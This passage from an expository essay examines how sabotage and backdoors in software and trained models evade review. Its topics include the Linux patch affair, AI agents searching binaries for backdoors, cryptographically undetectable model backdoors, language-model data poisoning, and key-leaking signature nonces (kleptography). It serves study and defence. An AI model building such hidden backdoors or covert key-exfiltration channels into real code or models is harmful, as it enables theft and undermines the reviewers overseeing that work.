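In April 2021 another faulty patch arrived from the University of Minnesota. *Intentionally buggy commits for fame—and papers* (Edge, 2021) reports that two developers questioned it and that Greg Kroah-Hartman, a senior maintainer, did not believe it was an honest mistake. He began reverting the university's earlier contributions. The researchers replied in *An open letter to the Linux community* (University of Minnesota, 2021) that the April patches belonged to a different project and that they had sent them,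 like 190 earlier ones, in good faith. Once Kroah-Hartman had reason to suspect the researchers, he could no longer tell their mistakes from sabotage by reading the code.

The board had to re-examine 435 changes, according to Tom's Hardware's *Linux Foundation Issues Frosty Final Judgment in UMN Scandal*. A reader's comment under LWN's *The TAB report on the UMN affair* (2021) says the board thanked 85 developers for helping. Another commenter says the reviewers kept the changes they found valid and removed or repaired the faulty ones. Maintainers had therefore accepted some faulty patches, though the people who submitted them say they meant no harm.

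Wu and Lu (2021) withdrew their paper before publication and called the study's design inappropriate because they had experimented on the Linux community without its consent. A secret trial large enough to measure a detection rate would raise the same objection more strongly. Project leaders could agree to a trial on behalf of their reviewers, as companies do when they test staff with fake phishing emails, but the reviewers might be more alert than usual.

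### Five simple checks on 40 vote counters

Wheeler tested whether simple tools and rules could catch underhanded code without relying on a reviewer's alertness. He used 40 vote-counting programs from the Obfuscated V contest, leaving out one because its published version contained no attack.

He then chose five countermeasures:

- run the program with AddressSanitizer, a tool that reports when a program reads or writes memory it should not;
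- restrict the use of macros in C;
- forbid names that a reader could confuse with numbers, such as a lower-case l or an upper-case O;
- use an editor that colours comments, and reformat the code so that nothing can follow a comment on the same line;
- compile with many of GCC's warnings turned on.

At least one of these caught 30 of the 40 programs, or 75 per cent. GCC should have caught another program for its misleading indentation, but the compiler's check had a bug, which Wheeler reported. He judged that six of the remaining nine would look suspicious to a reviewer, for example because they were oddly repetitive.

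The remaining three programs were neither caught nor suspicious. One filled in only part of a table, because its loop used the size of a different table with a similar name. Another converted a number to an unsuitable type. The third tested twice whether a vote was n, instead of testing for both n and N. Wheeler thinks new compiler warnings could catch all three kinds of mistake.

The 75 per cent figure has several limitations. Wheeler picked the countermeasures after he had studied the samples. He acknowledges this and says he only wanted to show that a few simple measures can often work. He did not run AddressSanitizer on every program, but worked out what it should report. Two of the published contest entries were his own. He alone judged which programs looked suspicious, and he already knew that all of them were malicious.

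Wheeler did not run the same checks on honest programs, so the false-alarm rate is unknown and could be high. Many of the vote counters also contain an unrelated mistake in how they print numbers, and honest programs often contain similar mistakes. Wheeler cites Les Hatton's study of MISRA C, a strict set of rules for programming in C. Hatton applied the 2004 edition to real code and found that far too few of the violations were genuine faults.

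The programmers were also not trying to get past these five checks. A saboteur who knows about them can compile the code with the same warnings enabled and keep changing it until none appears. The extra parentheses in the line someone tried to slip into Linux in 2003 silence one of these warnings.

### AI agents searching binaries

BinaryAudit, a benchmark from the software company Quesma, measures how well AI agents find backdoors in programs without seeing the source code. Grabowski, Strzaliński and colleagues (2026) describe it in *We hid backdoors in ~40 MB binaries and asked AI + Ghidra*. They added backdoors to open-source programs such as the web server lighttpd, the network program dnsmasq and the SSH server Dropbear. They then compiled the programs and gave the agents the binaries, along with Ghidra and Radare2, two free tools that turn machine code back into something like C. In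 most tasks, the agent had to give the address of the function containing the backdoor.

Grabowski and colleagues did not disguise the backdoors heavily and expected a skilled human analyst to find them relatively easily. The best model in their article, Claude Opus 4.6, solved 49 per cent of the tasks, followed by Gemini 3 Pro with 44 per cent and Claude Opus 4.5 with 37 per cent. In a few other tasks, the agent received three binaries and only had to pick out those with a backdoor. These tasks were meant to be easier but turned out not to be.

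Claude Opus 4.5 found the backdoor in lighttpd within five minutes. The backdoor looked for a made-up header in each web request and ran whatever command the header contained. Claude first searched the files for suspicious words and found none. It then listed the system functions each library used and saw that one used popen, which runs commands. Only one function called popen, and its name, li_check_debug_header, was still readable in the library. Claude noted that a "debug header" function had little reason to run commands, translated the function back into readable code and confirmed the backdoor. A more careful attacker would have removed the name or chosen a less revealing one.

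The backdoor in dnsmasq was seven lines long. Dnsmasq assigns network addresses to computers that request them, and a request can include numbered options. If a request included option 224, which the researchers had invented, the altered program ran the option's contents as a command. Claude Opus 4.6 found the right function and the call that runs the command, but decided it was probably dnsmasq's legitimate feature for running a script when it assigns an address. Claude moved on to other functions and never checked where the command came from. Checking would have shown that any computer on the network could supply it.

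Claude had the evidence but drew the wrong conclusion, partly because it knew enough about dnsmasq to think of an innocent explanation. Grabowski and colleagues had not planned this, but a saboteur could, by putting a backdoor next to a legitimate feature that does nearly the same thing. Tan did something similar by putting the xz payload among files that were meant to be damaged.

The agents also reported backdoors that did not exist. Grabowski and colleagues also gave them clean binaries, and across all models 28 per cent of the answers on these contained a false alarm. For example, Gemini 3 Pro reported that one server would run any command a user typed as the value of a particular time limit, but the server's source code reads that value as a number and never runs it.

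Results differed widely between models and settings. The results page for Quesma's *Can AI find backdoors in raw machine code?* lists 26 models and settings. Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview matched the top score of 49 per cent and raised false alarms on 17 per cent of clean binaries. OpenAI's GPT-5.2 Codex found 46 per cent with no false alarms at an extra-high effort setting, but only 9 per cent without that setting. A detection rate therefore applies to a model at a particular setting, and a reviewer who uses less computing may get a much lower rate.

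The benchmark has only 33 tasks, so a difference of a few percentage points between models means little. The tools also limited the agents. Ghidra and Radare2 worked so poorly on Go programs that the researchers excluded those programs, although a commercial tool worked well on one of them. The best score on Quesma's timeline is from a February 2026 model. Much stronger models released since then would probably do better on the same backdoors, but they might not do better on backdoors written by an equally strong model.

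### Why most alarms would be false

Grabowski and colleagues think that a practical tool would need a false-alarm rate below 0.001 per cent, because nearly all software is free of backdoors. Suppose that one program in 10,000 contains a backdoor, and that a checker detects 50 per cent of the backdoors and wrongly flags 1 per cent of clean programs. If it checks a million programs, the expected results are:

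| | Flagged | Not flagged |
|---|---|---|
| With a backdoor | 50 | 50 |
| Clean | 9,999 | 989,901 |

Of the 10,049 programs the checker flags, 50 (about 0.5 per cent) contain a backdoor. An analyst would have to investigate about 200 programs for each backdoor found, and may look less carefully after dismissing 150 false alarms.

Even if the checker caught every backdoor, the chance that a flagged program contained one would rise only to about 1 per cent. If it still caught half but wrongly flagged only 0.001 per cent of clean programs, the chance would rise to about 83 per cent. If it caught half and wrongly flagged 28 per cent of clean programs, the average for the BinaryAudit models, only about one flagged program in 5,600 would contain a backdoor.

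It is hard to show that a checker is good enough. GPT-5.2 Codex raised no false alarms, but it was tested on very few clean binaries. As a rule of thumb, if something has not happened in n independent trials, its rate is probably below 3/n. To show with reasonable confidence that the false-alarm rate is below 0.001 per cent, testers would need to run the checker on about 300,000 clean programs without a false alarm.

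False reports already take up maintainers' time. Grabowski and colleagues mention that the curl project, which makes a widely used data transfer tool, stopped paying for bug reports partly because it received so many worthless ones written with AI.

The probabilities change if there is good reason to suspect the author. Suppose that half of an author's programs contain a backdoor, and the checker is the same as before. A flagged program then has a 98 per cent chance of containing a backdoor, so false alarms are no longer much of a problem. But a program that passes still has a one in three chance of containing one. Anyone deciding whether to run that author's code would need a checker that misses far fewer backdoors.

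### Old bugs and bugs written to be missed

AI systems have begun to find accidental bugs in widely used software that experts had overlooked for years. Older automated tools do this too. Wu and Lu ran Syzkaller, which tests Linux with unusual sequences of system calls, on an ordinary desktop computer for a week, and it found 12 memory leaks in the latest version. Finding bugs that experts missed does not necessarily mean a system would also find flaws that a saboteur has hidden.

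A count of the flaws that reviewers and tools find, like a count of known backdoors, doesn't give a detection rate. Each repair still makes the software safer, but a saboteur needs only one flaw to go undetected.

A saboteur can also test flaws against detection tools in advance and adapt them to pass, which does not happen with accidental bugs. If a checker catches 95 per cent of planted flaws of some type, a saboteur who can run it in private could write 40 versions of a flaw, expect about two to pass, and submit one of those. The checker would then catch nothing that this saboteur submits, even though the 95 per cent figure is accurate. Wu and Lu did something similar by hand when they chose three promising places out of 200.

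A bug-finding tool can even help a saboteur. Wu and Lu expected maintainers to trust their second patch more because it addressed a memory leak that Syzkaller had reported. The patch did fix the leak, so a maintainer who checked for it would have found it gone.

Still, better bug finding makes it harder for a saboteur to keep deniability. To pass for an honest mistake, a flaw has to resemble the mistakes programmers really make, which bug finders are built to catch. Wheeler found that 25 of his 40 samples relied on one of five familiar problems, such as writing past the end of a table or confusing = with ==. A saboteur can avoid such tools by using a secret trigger, as in xz, but then loses deniability.

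Wheeler suggests that defenders publish some of their countermeasures and keep the details of others secret, so that an author cannot test a flaw against all of them. This works best against an author who has to run a checker to learn what it will catch. A superhuman author might be able to predict that from general knowledge of how such checkers work. If the reviewer is an AI, the author might also be a newer version of the same model.

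## What theory says about finding a hidden trigger in code

A saboteur can beat any particular checker by testing code against it in advance, and Henry Gordon Rice proved in 1951 that no checker can be perfect. His theorem covers semantic properties, which depend on what a program does, such as whether it ever opens a session without the user's password. Whether a program contains an if statement is not a semantic property, because it depends on how the program is written. If some programs have a semantic property and others lack it, no procedure can correctly decide for every program whether it has that property.

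Cohen (1984), in *Cure of Computer Viruses*, made a similar argument about viruses, programs that copy themselves into other programs. Suppose a procedure D always correctly reports whether a program is a virus. A program P could then run D on itself and infect other programs only if D classifies it as harmless. D is wrong either way, because P does nothing if D classifies it as a virus and spreads if D doesn't, so no such procedure can exist. The argument also applies to a program that opens a backdoor whenever D classifies it as harmless.

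### Refusing whatever is unclear

Both proofs concern a single procedure that must be right about every program, so neither settles what a reviewer can achieve. A reviewer can also reject a program without deciding what it does. For example, a rule against writing to other program files would stop P without anyone having to work out D's output for it. The rule would also stop compilers and installers, which write such files for good reasons.

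Rejecting every program would keep out every backdoor, so the practical question is how many harmless programs a safe rule rejects. Rice's theorem doesn't determine that number. Evans (2017) similarly concludes in *On the Impossibility of Virus Detection* that detection can work well in practice even though it is impossible in general.

The proofs also don't apply to a program that always finishes and takes inputs of limited length, because a tester could in principle try every input. But a routine that reads 32 bytes has 2²⁵⁶ possible inputs, far too many to try. The obstacle then is computing time, and cryptographers have developed ways to make a search take too long.

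### A branch that waits for one input

Suppose that a login program contains this line, where x is the password that the user typed:

```
if (equal(sha256(x), stored)) open_session();
```

SHA-256, a standard hash function, turns an input of almost any length into 256 bits that look random. The author chose a long random password and put only its hash in the source, as the constant "stored".

A random input has about one chance in 10⁷⁷ of matching. A tester trying a billion inputs a second for the age of the universe would test about 4 × 10²⁶. Testing tools that use near misses to choose the next input don't help, because changing one character of x changes the whole hash unpredictably.

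A reader of the line can't work out the password, because nobody knows a practical way to reverse SHA-256. In Thomas and Francillon's example, the password was visible in the code as the fixed string \_BACKDOOR\_. In both programs, though, the reader can see that some input opens a session without the normal check, and can delete the line without knowing what that input is.

The author could try to make the line look normal. Legitimate login programs also compare hashes, because storing users' passwords directly would be unsafe. But they usually look up the hash in the user's record, so a reviewer should ask why this one is a constant in the source.

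### Hiding the branch as well

In cryptography, obfuscation means rewriting a program so that nobody can understand it. In *Injecting Undetectable Backdoors in Obfuscated Neural Networks and Language Models*, Kalavasis, Karbasi and colleagues (2024) require the new program to behave the same as the old one, run about as efficiently, and be very hard to understand even if the original was clear.

Indistinguishability obfuscation, or iO, makes the last requirement precise. If two programs of the same size give the same output for every input, and one of them is obfuscated, no efficient test can determine which one it was. An efficient test is one whose running time grows no faster than some fixed power of the problem's size. Barak and colleagues began the study of iO in 2001, and in 2021 Jain, Lin and Sahai built it from well-studied assumptions about which problems are hard. It is still far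 too slow for practical use, according to *Statistically Undetectable Backdoors in Deep Neural Networks* (Bogdanov, Rosen and Vafa, 2026).

This guarantee alone doesn't hide a backdoor, because a program with a backdoor behaves differently on the trigger. Christiano, Hilton and colleagues (2024), in *Backdoor defense, learnability and obfuscation*, get round this with a function F that uses a secret key K to turn each input into a bit that looks random. The author can "puncture" the key at the trigger t. The punctured key gives the right bit for every other input but reveals nothing about the bit for t. Now consider three programs, each of which the author obfuscates:

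```
clean:       return F(K, x)
halfway:     if x = t, return the correct bit for t
             otherwise return F(punctured K, x)
backdoored:  if x = t, return the wrong bit for t
             otherwise return F(punctured K, x)
```

The clean and halfway programs always give the same output, so iO makes them indistinguishable, even though only one contains a branch. The halfway and backdoored programs differ in a single stored bit. To tell whether that bit is correct, a test would have to predict F at t from the punctured key, which no efficient test can do. So no efficient test can tell the clean program from the backdoored one, even if the tester already knows t.

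Besides iO, the proof assumes that one-way functions exist. These are easy to calculate but infeasible to reverse, as SHA-256 appears to be.

A reviewer who insists on readable code would reject all three programs, including the clean one. The reviewer could also ask for the original source and the random numbers the obfuscator used, then rerun it and compare the results, as with a reproducible build.

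### Backdoors in trained models

A neural network's behaviour depends on many numbers, called weights, which training adjusts automatically. Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues (2022), in *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models*, imagine a bank that pays a company to train a network to approve or reject loans. The company then charges applicants to learn which small changes to their details, perhaps to the last digits of the loan amount, will guarantee approval.

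Goldwasser and colleagues call a backdoor in a machine-learning model undetectable if no efficient test can tell the altered model from an honestly trained one noticeably better than by guessing. In the black-box version, the tester can only submit inputs and look at the outputs. In the white-box version, the tester receives the complete model, including every weight.

Their simplest backdoor resembles the SHA-256 branch. It divides the input values into n groups and checks whether the number of non-negative values in each group is odd or even. If the results match a secret pattern, the backdoor takes over the output. A given input matches a randomly chosen pattern with probability 2⁻ⁿ, but someone who knows the pattern can make any input match by changing the sign of at most n values. Anyone who inspects the network can find the check and learn the pattern.

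A stronger version replaces the pattern with a digital signature and, like the xz backdoor, activates only on inputs signed with the attacker's private key. This works with any model and assumes only that one-way functions exist. Even with all the weights, nobody without the private key can efficiently find an input on which the altered and original models differ. The signature check may still be visible in the network's structure, so Goldwasser and colleagues claim only black-box undetectability for this version.

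### The backdoor that survives full inspection

Their white-box construction uses a simple type of network called a random Fourier features model. Each unit in its single hidden layer has a list of random numbers g and a random shift b. For an input x, the unit calculates

cos(2π(g · x + b))

where g · x means multiplying the two lists item by item and adding the results. Training sets only how much weight each unit gets in the final sum. The model answers yes if that sum is positive and no if it is negative.

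An honest trainer draws the numbers in g from the normal distribution, or bell curve. A malicious trainer first picks a secret list k, then draws each g so that g · k is almost exactly a whole number plus a half. To use the backdoor, an applicant adds k to the input. This adds an odd multiple of π to the angle inside every cosine. Because cos(θ + π) = −cos θ, every unit's output changes sign, and so does the final sum, which turns a no into a yes.

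An inspector who knew k could check this immediately. Without k, the inspector would have to notice that the lists follow a pattern in one unknown direction among a great many. Goldwasser and colleagues prove that an efficient way to do this would also solve certain problems about lattices, which are regular grids of points in many dimensions. Cryptographers expect these problems to be hard even for quantum computers, and base new encryption standards on them. The limit applies to any inspector, human or AI, however skilled, unless somebody finds a fast method for the lattice problems. A similar backdoor, for networks with a different kind of unit, relies on the hardness of another problem, sparse PCA.

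The trainer changes only the random numbers, so it can still use the client's data and run the agreed training program exactly. A client who checked every step of the training would still miss the backdoor unless they also controlled those numbers. The constants of Dual EC posed the same problem.

This backdoor has several weaknesses. Anyone who sees one input before and after the change can subtract one version from the other to get k, then use it on other inputs. *Undetectable Backdoors in Model Parameters* (2026) points out that the proof covers only single-layer networks with weights from a known distribution, and that nobody had tried the construction on a real architecture. Bogdanov and colleagues add that an outsider without k can efficiently find input changes that work even better, so the secret gives its owner no real advantage.

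### Later constructions

Bogdanov and colleagues built a backdoor that gives its owner an advantage and that no test can reliably detect, however much computing power the tester has. The owner knows a secret list z. Adding z to any input should change the output noticeably, but the backdoor leaves the output almost unchanged. In a face recognition system, for example, this might make two different people look alike.

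Honest models of this type also contain pairs of inputs with nearly identical outputs, but finding them would take too long. The malicious trainer knows such pairs because they generate the first layer together with z. Honest and malicious models differ almost entirely in what their trainers know, so there is very little in the model to detect. The proof requires whole-number inputs and a first layer that greatly compresses its input, using random weights that stay fixed during training. The later layers must also roughly preserve distances. Many ordinary networks don't meet these conditions.

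Kalavasis and colleagues use iO to hide backdoors in a much wider range of networks, but the method works only if honest trainers also obfuscate their models before release. They suggest companies might do this to protect trade secrets or private training data. Other researchers have tried to hide backdoors in modern image classifiers. *Backdoor Channels Hidden in Latent Space* (2026) notes that several earlier constructions evade selected defences but have no proof of white-box undetectability.

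### A game between attacker and defender

In these results, the inspector has a model but no suspicious input. Christiano and colleagues make the defender's task easier by supplying an input and asking whether it is the trigger. Their game has four steps:

1. The attacker chooses a clean program f from an agreed class, and decides how likely each input is.
2. A random draw from those inputs picks the trigger.
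3. The attacker chooses a second program from the class, f\*, which must differ from f on the trigger but on no more than a small fraction ε of inputs overall.
4. The defender receives either f with a random input or f\* with the trigger, each with probability one half, and has to say which.

The defender can read the whole program. The attacker must choose the original program, f, before learning the trigger. An attacker who already knew the trigger could put a special case at that input in f and at a different input in the backdoored version, f\*. Whichever program the defender received would then have one special case, unrelated to the input that came with it, and the defender could only guess. A real saboteur can choose the trigger freely, so a defence that works in this game might fail in practice.

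With unlimited computing time, the outcome depends on the class's VC dimension, a measure of how varied its programs are. This is the largest number of inputs for which programs in the class can produce every possible combination of yes and no answers. The defender almost always wins if ε is much smaller than 1 divided by the VC dimension. If the VC dimension is 1,000 and f\* differs on one input in a billion, the defender's chance of error is on the order of one in a million.

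To win, the defender collects sample answers from the suspicious program and uses them to predict the answer for the given input. The defender repeats this with fresh samples and takes a majority vote. The samples rarely include an altered answer, so the vote nearly always matches f's answer. If the program's answer differs from the vote, the input is probably the trigger.

The general method takes far too long to run, but a fast version exists for any class of programs that can be learned efficiently from examples. If one-way functions and indistinguishability obfuscation (iO) exist, programs in general have no fast defence, because an attacker can use the punctured-key construction, against which no efficient defender does noticeably better than guessing.

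### Defences that read the program

A defender can sometimes do better by looking at how a program reaches its answer. Christiano and colleagues give an example in which nobody can efficiently learn the programs from their answers, but each program openly states one special case. The defender only has to check whether the given input is that case. The SHA-256 branch is just as easy to check, because the defender can hash the input and compare.

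Their more natural example is a decision tree, which checks the input one bit at a time. Suppose that all inputs are equally likely and that the trees have at most 1,000 endpoints. The chance that a random input requires 30 or more checks is at most 1,000/2³⁰, or about one in a million. The clean tree therefore almost certainly needs fewer than 30 checks to process the trigger.

If the backdoored tree also needed fewer than 30 questions to classify the trigger input, the two trees would disagree on every input that gave the same answers to both trees' questions, which is at least one input in 2⁵⁸. An attacker who may change the output on a smaller fraction of inputs has to put the trigger behind a longer series of questions. The defender can count the questions and reject the input if there are too many.

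A clever author can avoid leaving such an obvious sign. Thomas Read found a family of logical formulas for this purpose, and the version with four inputs is:

```
clean:       d and c
backdoored:  (((a or (d and b)) and b) or (d and c)) and c
```

The two formulas differ only when a, b and c are true and d is false. The trigger becomes rarer as the formulas get longer. But every "and" and "or" in the backdoored formula receives each combination of true and false for at least one in eight random inputs, so a search for rarely used parts finds nothing.

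Multiplying out the brackets turns the backdoored formula into "(a and b and c) or (d and c)", which shows the extra condition. A reviewer could also reject the long version because the task needs only "d and c". Christiano and colleagues suggest rewriting formulas before checking them, but have no general defence of this kind.

The difficulty of learning from examples also limits some attackers. Many attacks on AI models add harmful examples to the training data. *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic* (Kaneko, 2026) considers attackers who can convey the secret trigger rule only through the labels of such examples. If the model can learn the rule in training, a defender with as many labelled examples can learn it by running the same training. An attacker therefore can't use this method to plant a rule that is too hard to learn.

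In Kaneko's experiments on four language models, the models learned an easy secret, which the defender recovered, but they did not learn a hard one, and the defender did not recover it either. The defender still needs examples of the trigger, which may be difficult to get. The backdoors by Goldwasser and colleagues avoid this limit on hard secrets because the attacker tampers with the random numbers or the network itself.

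### Undetectable is not the same as unsuspicious

In these proofs, a backdoored program is undetectable if no efficient test can distinguish it from the honest alternative. An obfuscated program with a backdoor can therefore go undetected when honest programs are also obfuscated, but it stands out when honest programmers submit readable code, which a reviewer can reasonably demand.

Nobody can make the same demand of a trained network, because even honest training produces a long list of numbers that no one can fully explain. Rejecting every unreadable network would mean rejecting all of them.

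Underhanded code, by contrast, is good at misleading human readers, but a tool may catch it easily. Åkesson's program for comparing warheads looked innocent to a reader, but a linker that compared types between files would have exposed it at once. The cryptographic proofs don't limit how well an author can mislead a reader, because there is no mathematical definition of code that looks innocent. They also don't show that a superhuman author could do it in any program.

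Readable programs can also contain unreadable parts, such as tables of constants or a small trained neural network. A reviewer can ask for constants that follow from a public formula. For a neural network, the reviewer can supply the random numbers used in training and then repeat the training, given the data and enough computing power.

Goldwasser and colleagues also describe a way to weaken a backdoor without finding it. The user makes several copies of each input, adds different random noise to each copy, and averages the model's answers. This cancels the effect of small changes an attacker makes to the input to trigger the backdoor. More noise protects against larger changes but makes the model less accurate. An attacker who knows how much noise to expect can also design a backdoor that needs a larger change.

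## What an author can hide inside a satisfied specification

Rice's theorem and the cryptographic results limit what a reviewer can find by examining a finished program, but the reviewer can also ask the author to prove that the program is safe. *Proof-Carrying Code* (Necula, 1997) describes how a computer could use such proofs to decide whether to run a stranger's program. The user publishes safety rules in advance, the author sends a proof that the program follows them, and the computer runs the program only if the proof is valid.

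### Proofs from an untrusted author

The proof is about the machine code itself. The user's computer builds a logical formula from the instructions, called the verification condition, whose truth guarantees that the program follows the rules. If an instruction reads memory at the address in register r plus 8, for example, the formula includes the claim that the program may read r + 8. For each loop, the author supplies a statement that should hold at the start of every pass, and the formula includes the claims that the statement holds on the first pass and that each pass preserves it. The author proves the whole formula, and a proof checker on the user's computer verifies every step.

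The user has to trust only the safety rules and the software that builds the formula and checks the proof. That software can be small, since a simple version of the checker's core takes a couple of pages of code. Necula considered cryptographic signatures a weaker safeguard, because even a trusted person can make mistakes or act maliciously. If someone alters a program or its proof in transit, the check will usually fail, and if it still succeeds, the altered program also obeys the rules.

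A rare trigger does not help the author, because the proof covers every input. No tester would find the password behind the SHA-256 branch in the login program, but the author could not prove that the program never opens a session without the user's own password, because the hidden password makes that false. A proof about machine code also covers anything the compiler introduced, such as the backdoor that a Clang bug created from a harmless patch to sudo. An attacker could still use Thompson's method on the compiler that built the proof checker.

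The choice of rules determines which contest tricks would fail. Necula's examples have rules about memory and types, and similar rules would exclude Colbus's call that overwrote a debugging flag. Blackburn's overflow stays inside one record, so the rules would exclude it only if they protected each field separately. Åkesson's warhead program reads only its own memory, but it treats eight-byte numbers as four-byte ones, which a rule about types would exclude. RHays's digit zero and the NaN entries break no rule about memory or types. To exclude them, the rules would have to state what the program must do, for instance answer yes only if the score reaches the threshold.

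Most of the burden falls on the author. Necula's programs were short, and he doubted that his way of producing proofs would work for programs of realistic size. He expected compilers to generate proofs of simpler properties, such as type safety. Once a proof exists, the burden on the user is very small. In *Safe Kernel Extensions Without Run-Time Checking* (1996), Necula and Lee had already applied the idea to programs that run inside an operating system's kernel. Necula reports that packet filters (programs that select network traffic for an application) with proofs ran ten times faster than equivalent filters in the usual interpreted language, because they were written in hand-tuned assembly language.

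### The redacted image

The winner of the 2008 Underhanded C Contest leaked information without breaking any memory rule, and his method would even satisfy a natural specification of the task. Entrants had to black out rectangles in an image in such a way that someone could recover the hidden part. John Meacham's program was 55 lines long. It used a text format that stores each pixel as three numbers from 0 to 255, for red, green and blue. Inside the rectangle, the program replaced every digit with a zero. For a black, a dark grey and a white pixel, the result is:

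```
before:   0 0 0    87 87 87    255 255 255
after:    0 0 0    00 00 00    000 000 000
```

Any image viewer reads 0, 00 and 000 as the same number and shows a black rectangle. But in a scan of black print on white paper, the ink becomes 0 and the paper becomes 000, so anyone who opens the file as text can reconstruct the words.

Suppose the specification requires pixels outside the rectangle to keep their values and every value inside to be zero. Meacham's method satisfies both requirements, and a proof checker would be right to accept a proof that it does. The specification would have ruled out the program by the runner-up, Avinash Baliga, which left two bits of each value intact, but not Åkesson's entry in the same contest, which added the original image after the last pixel.

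A specification of the exact bytes stops Meacham's trick. It could require every number inside the rectangle to be written as a single 0. The format also permits extra spaces and comments, so the specification has to define those exactly too, and forbid anything after the last pixel.

That is easy for such a simple format, but a compressed format such as PNG can store the same pixels in a vast number of files. An exact specification would have to settle every choice the compressor makes, and any later improvement to the compressor would need a new specification and a new proof. The user could instead pass the image through a small separate program that reads the pixel values and writes them out in one fixed way. This leaves the author free to change the main program, but the small program also needs a proof, and its files may be larger than necessary.

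### Counting the hidden bits

If a specification allows N different outputs for some input, a hostile program can send one of N messages by choosing which output to produce. A single run can therefore carry up to log₂ N hidden bits, or none if only one output is allowed. The recipient may get fewer bits, because they have to see the output and work out which choice the program made.

A rectangle of 1,000 pixels contains 3,000 numbers. If the program may write each number as one, two or three zeros, there are 3³⁰⁰⁰ permitted outputs, enough to encode about 4,755 bits, or roughly 100 English words. Meacham used these choices to record how bright each pixel had been, but a program could also use them to record a password it found elsewhere in memory.

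The leaked bits add up over repeated runs, so even a single free choice per run can eventually reveal any secret that doesn't change. Cryptographic keys are especially useful targets because they are short, often 256 bits, and give access to far more data than they contain.

### Signatures that carry the key

A digital signature shows that the holder of a private key approved a message. Gustavus Simmons discovered that many signature methods also let the signer hide information in the signature, which he called a subliminal channel. According to *The Newton Channel*, by Anderson, Vaudenay and colleagues, the problem came up in nuclear arms control. The United States and the Soviet Union planned to put sensors in each other's nuclear facilities, with safeguards to keep anyone from altering the readings. In one early design, a sensor meant to report only whether a silo held a missile could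 also have revealed the silo's location, which would help in a first strike.

DSA, the method that Birr-Pixton attacked in the 2015 cryptography contest, calculates a signature (r, s) like this:

r = (gᵏ mod p) mod q
s = (h + x·r) / k mod q

Here g, p and q are public numbers, x is the private key, h is a hash of the message, and k is the nonce, a fresh random number. "Mod" means the remainder after division, and the division by k is also done among remainders. Almost any k produces a valid signature. In the original DSA, q has 160 bits, so each message has nearly 2¹⁶⁰ valid signatures.

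A hostile program can leak the key one bit at a time. It picks a k, calculates r, and checks whether the last bit of r equals the next bit of the key. If not, it picks another k. Half of all values of k give a match, so this takes two tries on average. Bitcoin wallets use the elliptic-curve version of DSA, which works similarly. Its keys are 256 bits long, so 256 signatures reveal the whole key. 21 Analytics demonstrates such a leak with a short program. Every signature is valid, so the program satisfies the specification "each output is a valid signature of the message".

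The program can leak more bits at once by trying more values of k:

| Hidden bits per signature | Average tries per signature | Signatures needed for a 256-bit key |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 2 | 256 |
| 4 | 16 | 64 |
| 8 | 256 | 32 |
| 16 | 65,536 | 16 |

A participant in *Non interactive anti-exfil (airgap compatible)*, a forum discussion about Bitcoin wallets, thinks that even a small device could leak four bits per signature. The device can first expand the key into several gigabytes of error-correcting data, then use each signature to leak a few bits from a position that depends on the message. The attacker can recover the key from any large enough set of signatures, in any order.

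A recipient who knows the private key can receive far more, because the signer can use the hidden message as k and the recipient can calculate k from the signature. In ElGamal signatures, which resemble DSA, anyone can recover part of k even without the private key if p − 1 has many small factors. Anderson and colleagues found that one prime suggested in the original DSA proposal would have allowed about 352 hidden bits in each ElGamal signature. DSA removes this channel by restricting the calculation to a group whose size is the prime q.

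### Leaking a key to one person only

If the last bits of r simply spell out the key, anyone who suspects the trick can read it. The device can encrypt the bits first, but then it has to contain the encryption key, and whoever takes the device apart can find it there. Young and Yung, in *The Prevalence of Kleptographic Attacks on Discrete-Log Based Cryptosystems*, avoid this by putting only the attacker's public key in the device. In simplified form, the attacker keeps a secret number X and the device contains Y = gˣ, with that X as the exponent. The attack then needs two signatures:

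1. The device makes the first signature with a random nonce, k₁. Anyone can calculate g to the power k₁ from the signature and the signer's public key.
2. The device raises Y to the power k₁ and hashes the result to get k₂, the nonce for the second signature.
3. The attacker raises the number from the first signature to the power X. This gives the same result, because both calculations multiply the exponents X and k₁, so the attacker also gets k₂.
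4. The attacker calculates the private key from the second signature: x = (s·k₂ − h) / r mod q.

Someone who takes the device apart will find the attacker's public key Y but not the private key X, so they can't work out the keys the device has leaked. The xz backdoor used a public key in the same way. Young and Yung add further secret values so that even the owner of the private signing key can't recognize the pattern from the signatures. The device can also send any 160 bits in the same two signatures. Simmons's channel in DSA carried about 14 bits per signature.

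Young and Yung call the study of such attacks kleptography. By their definition, the altered device must conform to the public specification, and its output must look normal to everyone except the attacker. Dark Skippy, a more recent attack on Bitcoin hardware wallets, needs only two transactions to leak a seed phrase, according to CryptoSlate's *How malicious hardware wallet firmware can leak your Bitcoin seed phrase*.

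Changing keys often enough would defeat a leak of one bit per signature, but not one that needs only two signatures. Changing keys also fails if the device leaks the master secret from which it derives all its keys. Blockstream's *Anti-Exfil* gives an example in which a few hundred signatures are enough to leak that secret, even if they come from different keys.

### What deterministic signing does and does not fix

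Deterministic signing removes the choice of k by calculating it from the private key and the message with a fixed formula, such as the one in RFC 6979. Each message then has only one permitted signature, so the signature can carry log₂ 1 = 0 hidden bits. If the author proves that the code follows the formula exactly, the channel is closed.

Without such a proof, the formula protects only against honest mistakes. Poelstra (2023), in *Anti-Exfiltration for EC Signatures*, notes that deterministic nonces prevent accidental bias and reuse. But the owner of a sealed hardware wallet cannot verify from outside that it follows the formula. To check k, the owner would have to repeat the calculation on another computer, which requires the private key that the wallet is supposed to keep off other computers.

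Some signature methods, including certain forms of RSA, accept only one signature for each message, so anyone can confirm from the signature itself that the device could not have produced a different valid one. But users have to switch to a different method, often one with larger signatures.

Another remedy is to have the user's computer contribute to k, so that the device cannot choose it alone. This takes extra communication, which is awkward for wallets that people deliberately keep disconnected. One participant in *Non interactive anti-exfil (airgap compatible)* also warns that malicious hardware could leak by radio or another side channel, which this remedy doesn't cover.

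Determinism creates its own risk. *The Dark Side of Deterministic Signatures* describes libraries for EdDSA, a deterministic signature method, that have the caller supply the public key separately. An attacker who can request signatures on the same message with two different public keys gets two equations with the same nonce and can solve them for the private key. The libraries can prevent this by calculating the public key themselves, which takes a little more computation.

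### Secrecy lost in refinement

The same problem arises in refinement, where programmers start from a loose specification and gradually replace its free choices with definite ones. Suppose a program holds one secret bit and its specification requires only that it output 0 or 1. At this stage an observer learns nothing about the secret from the output, because either output could occur with either secret. A programmer can then write code that outputs the secret bit, which satisfies the specification but reveals the secret.

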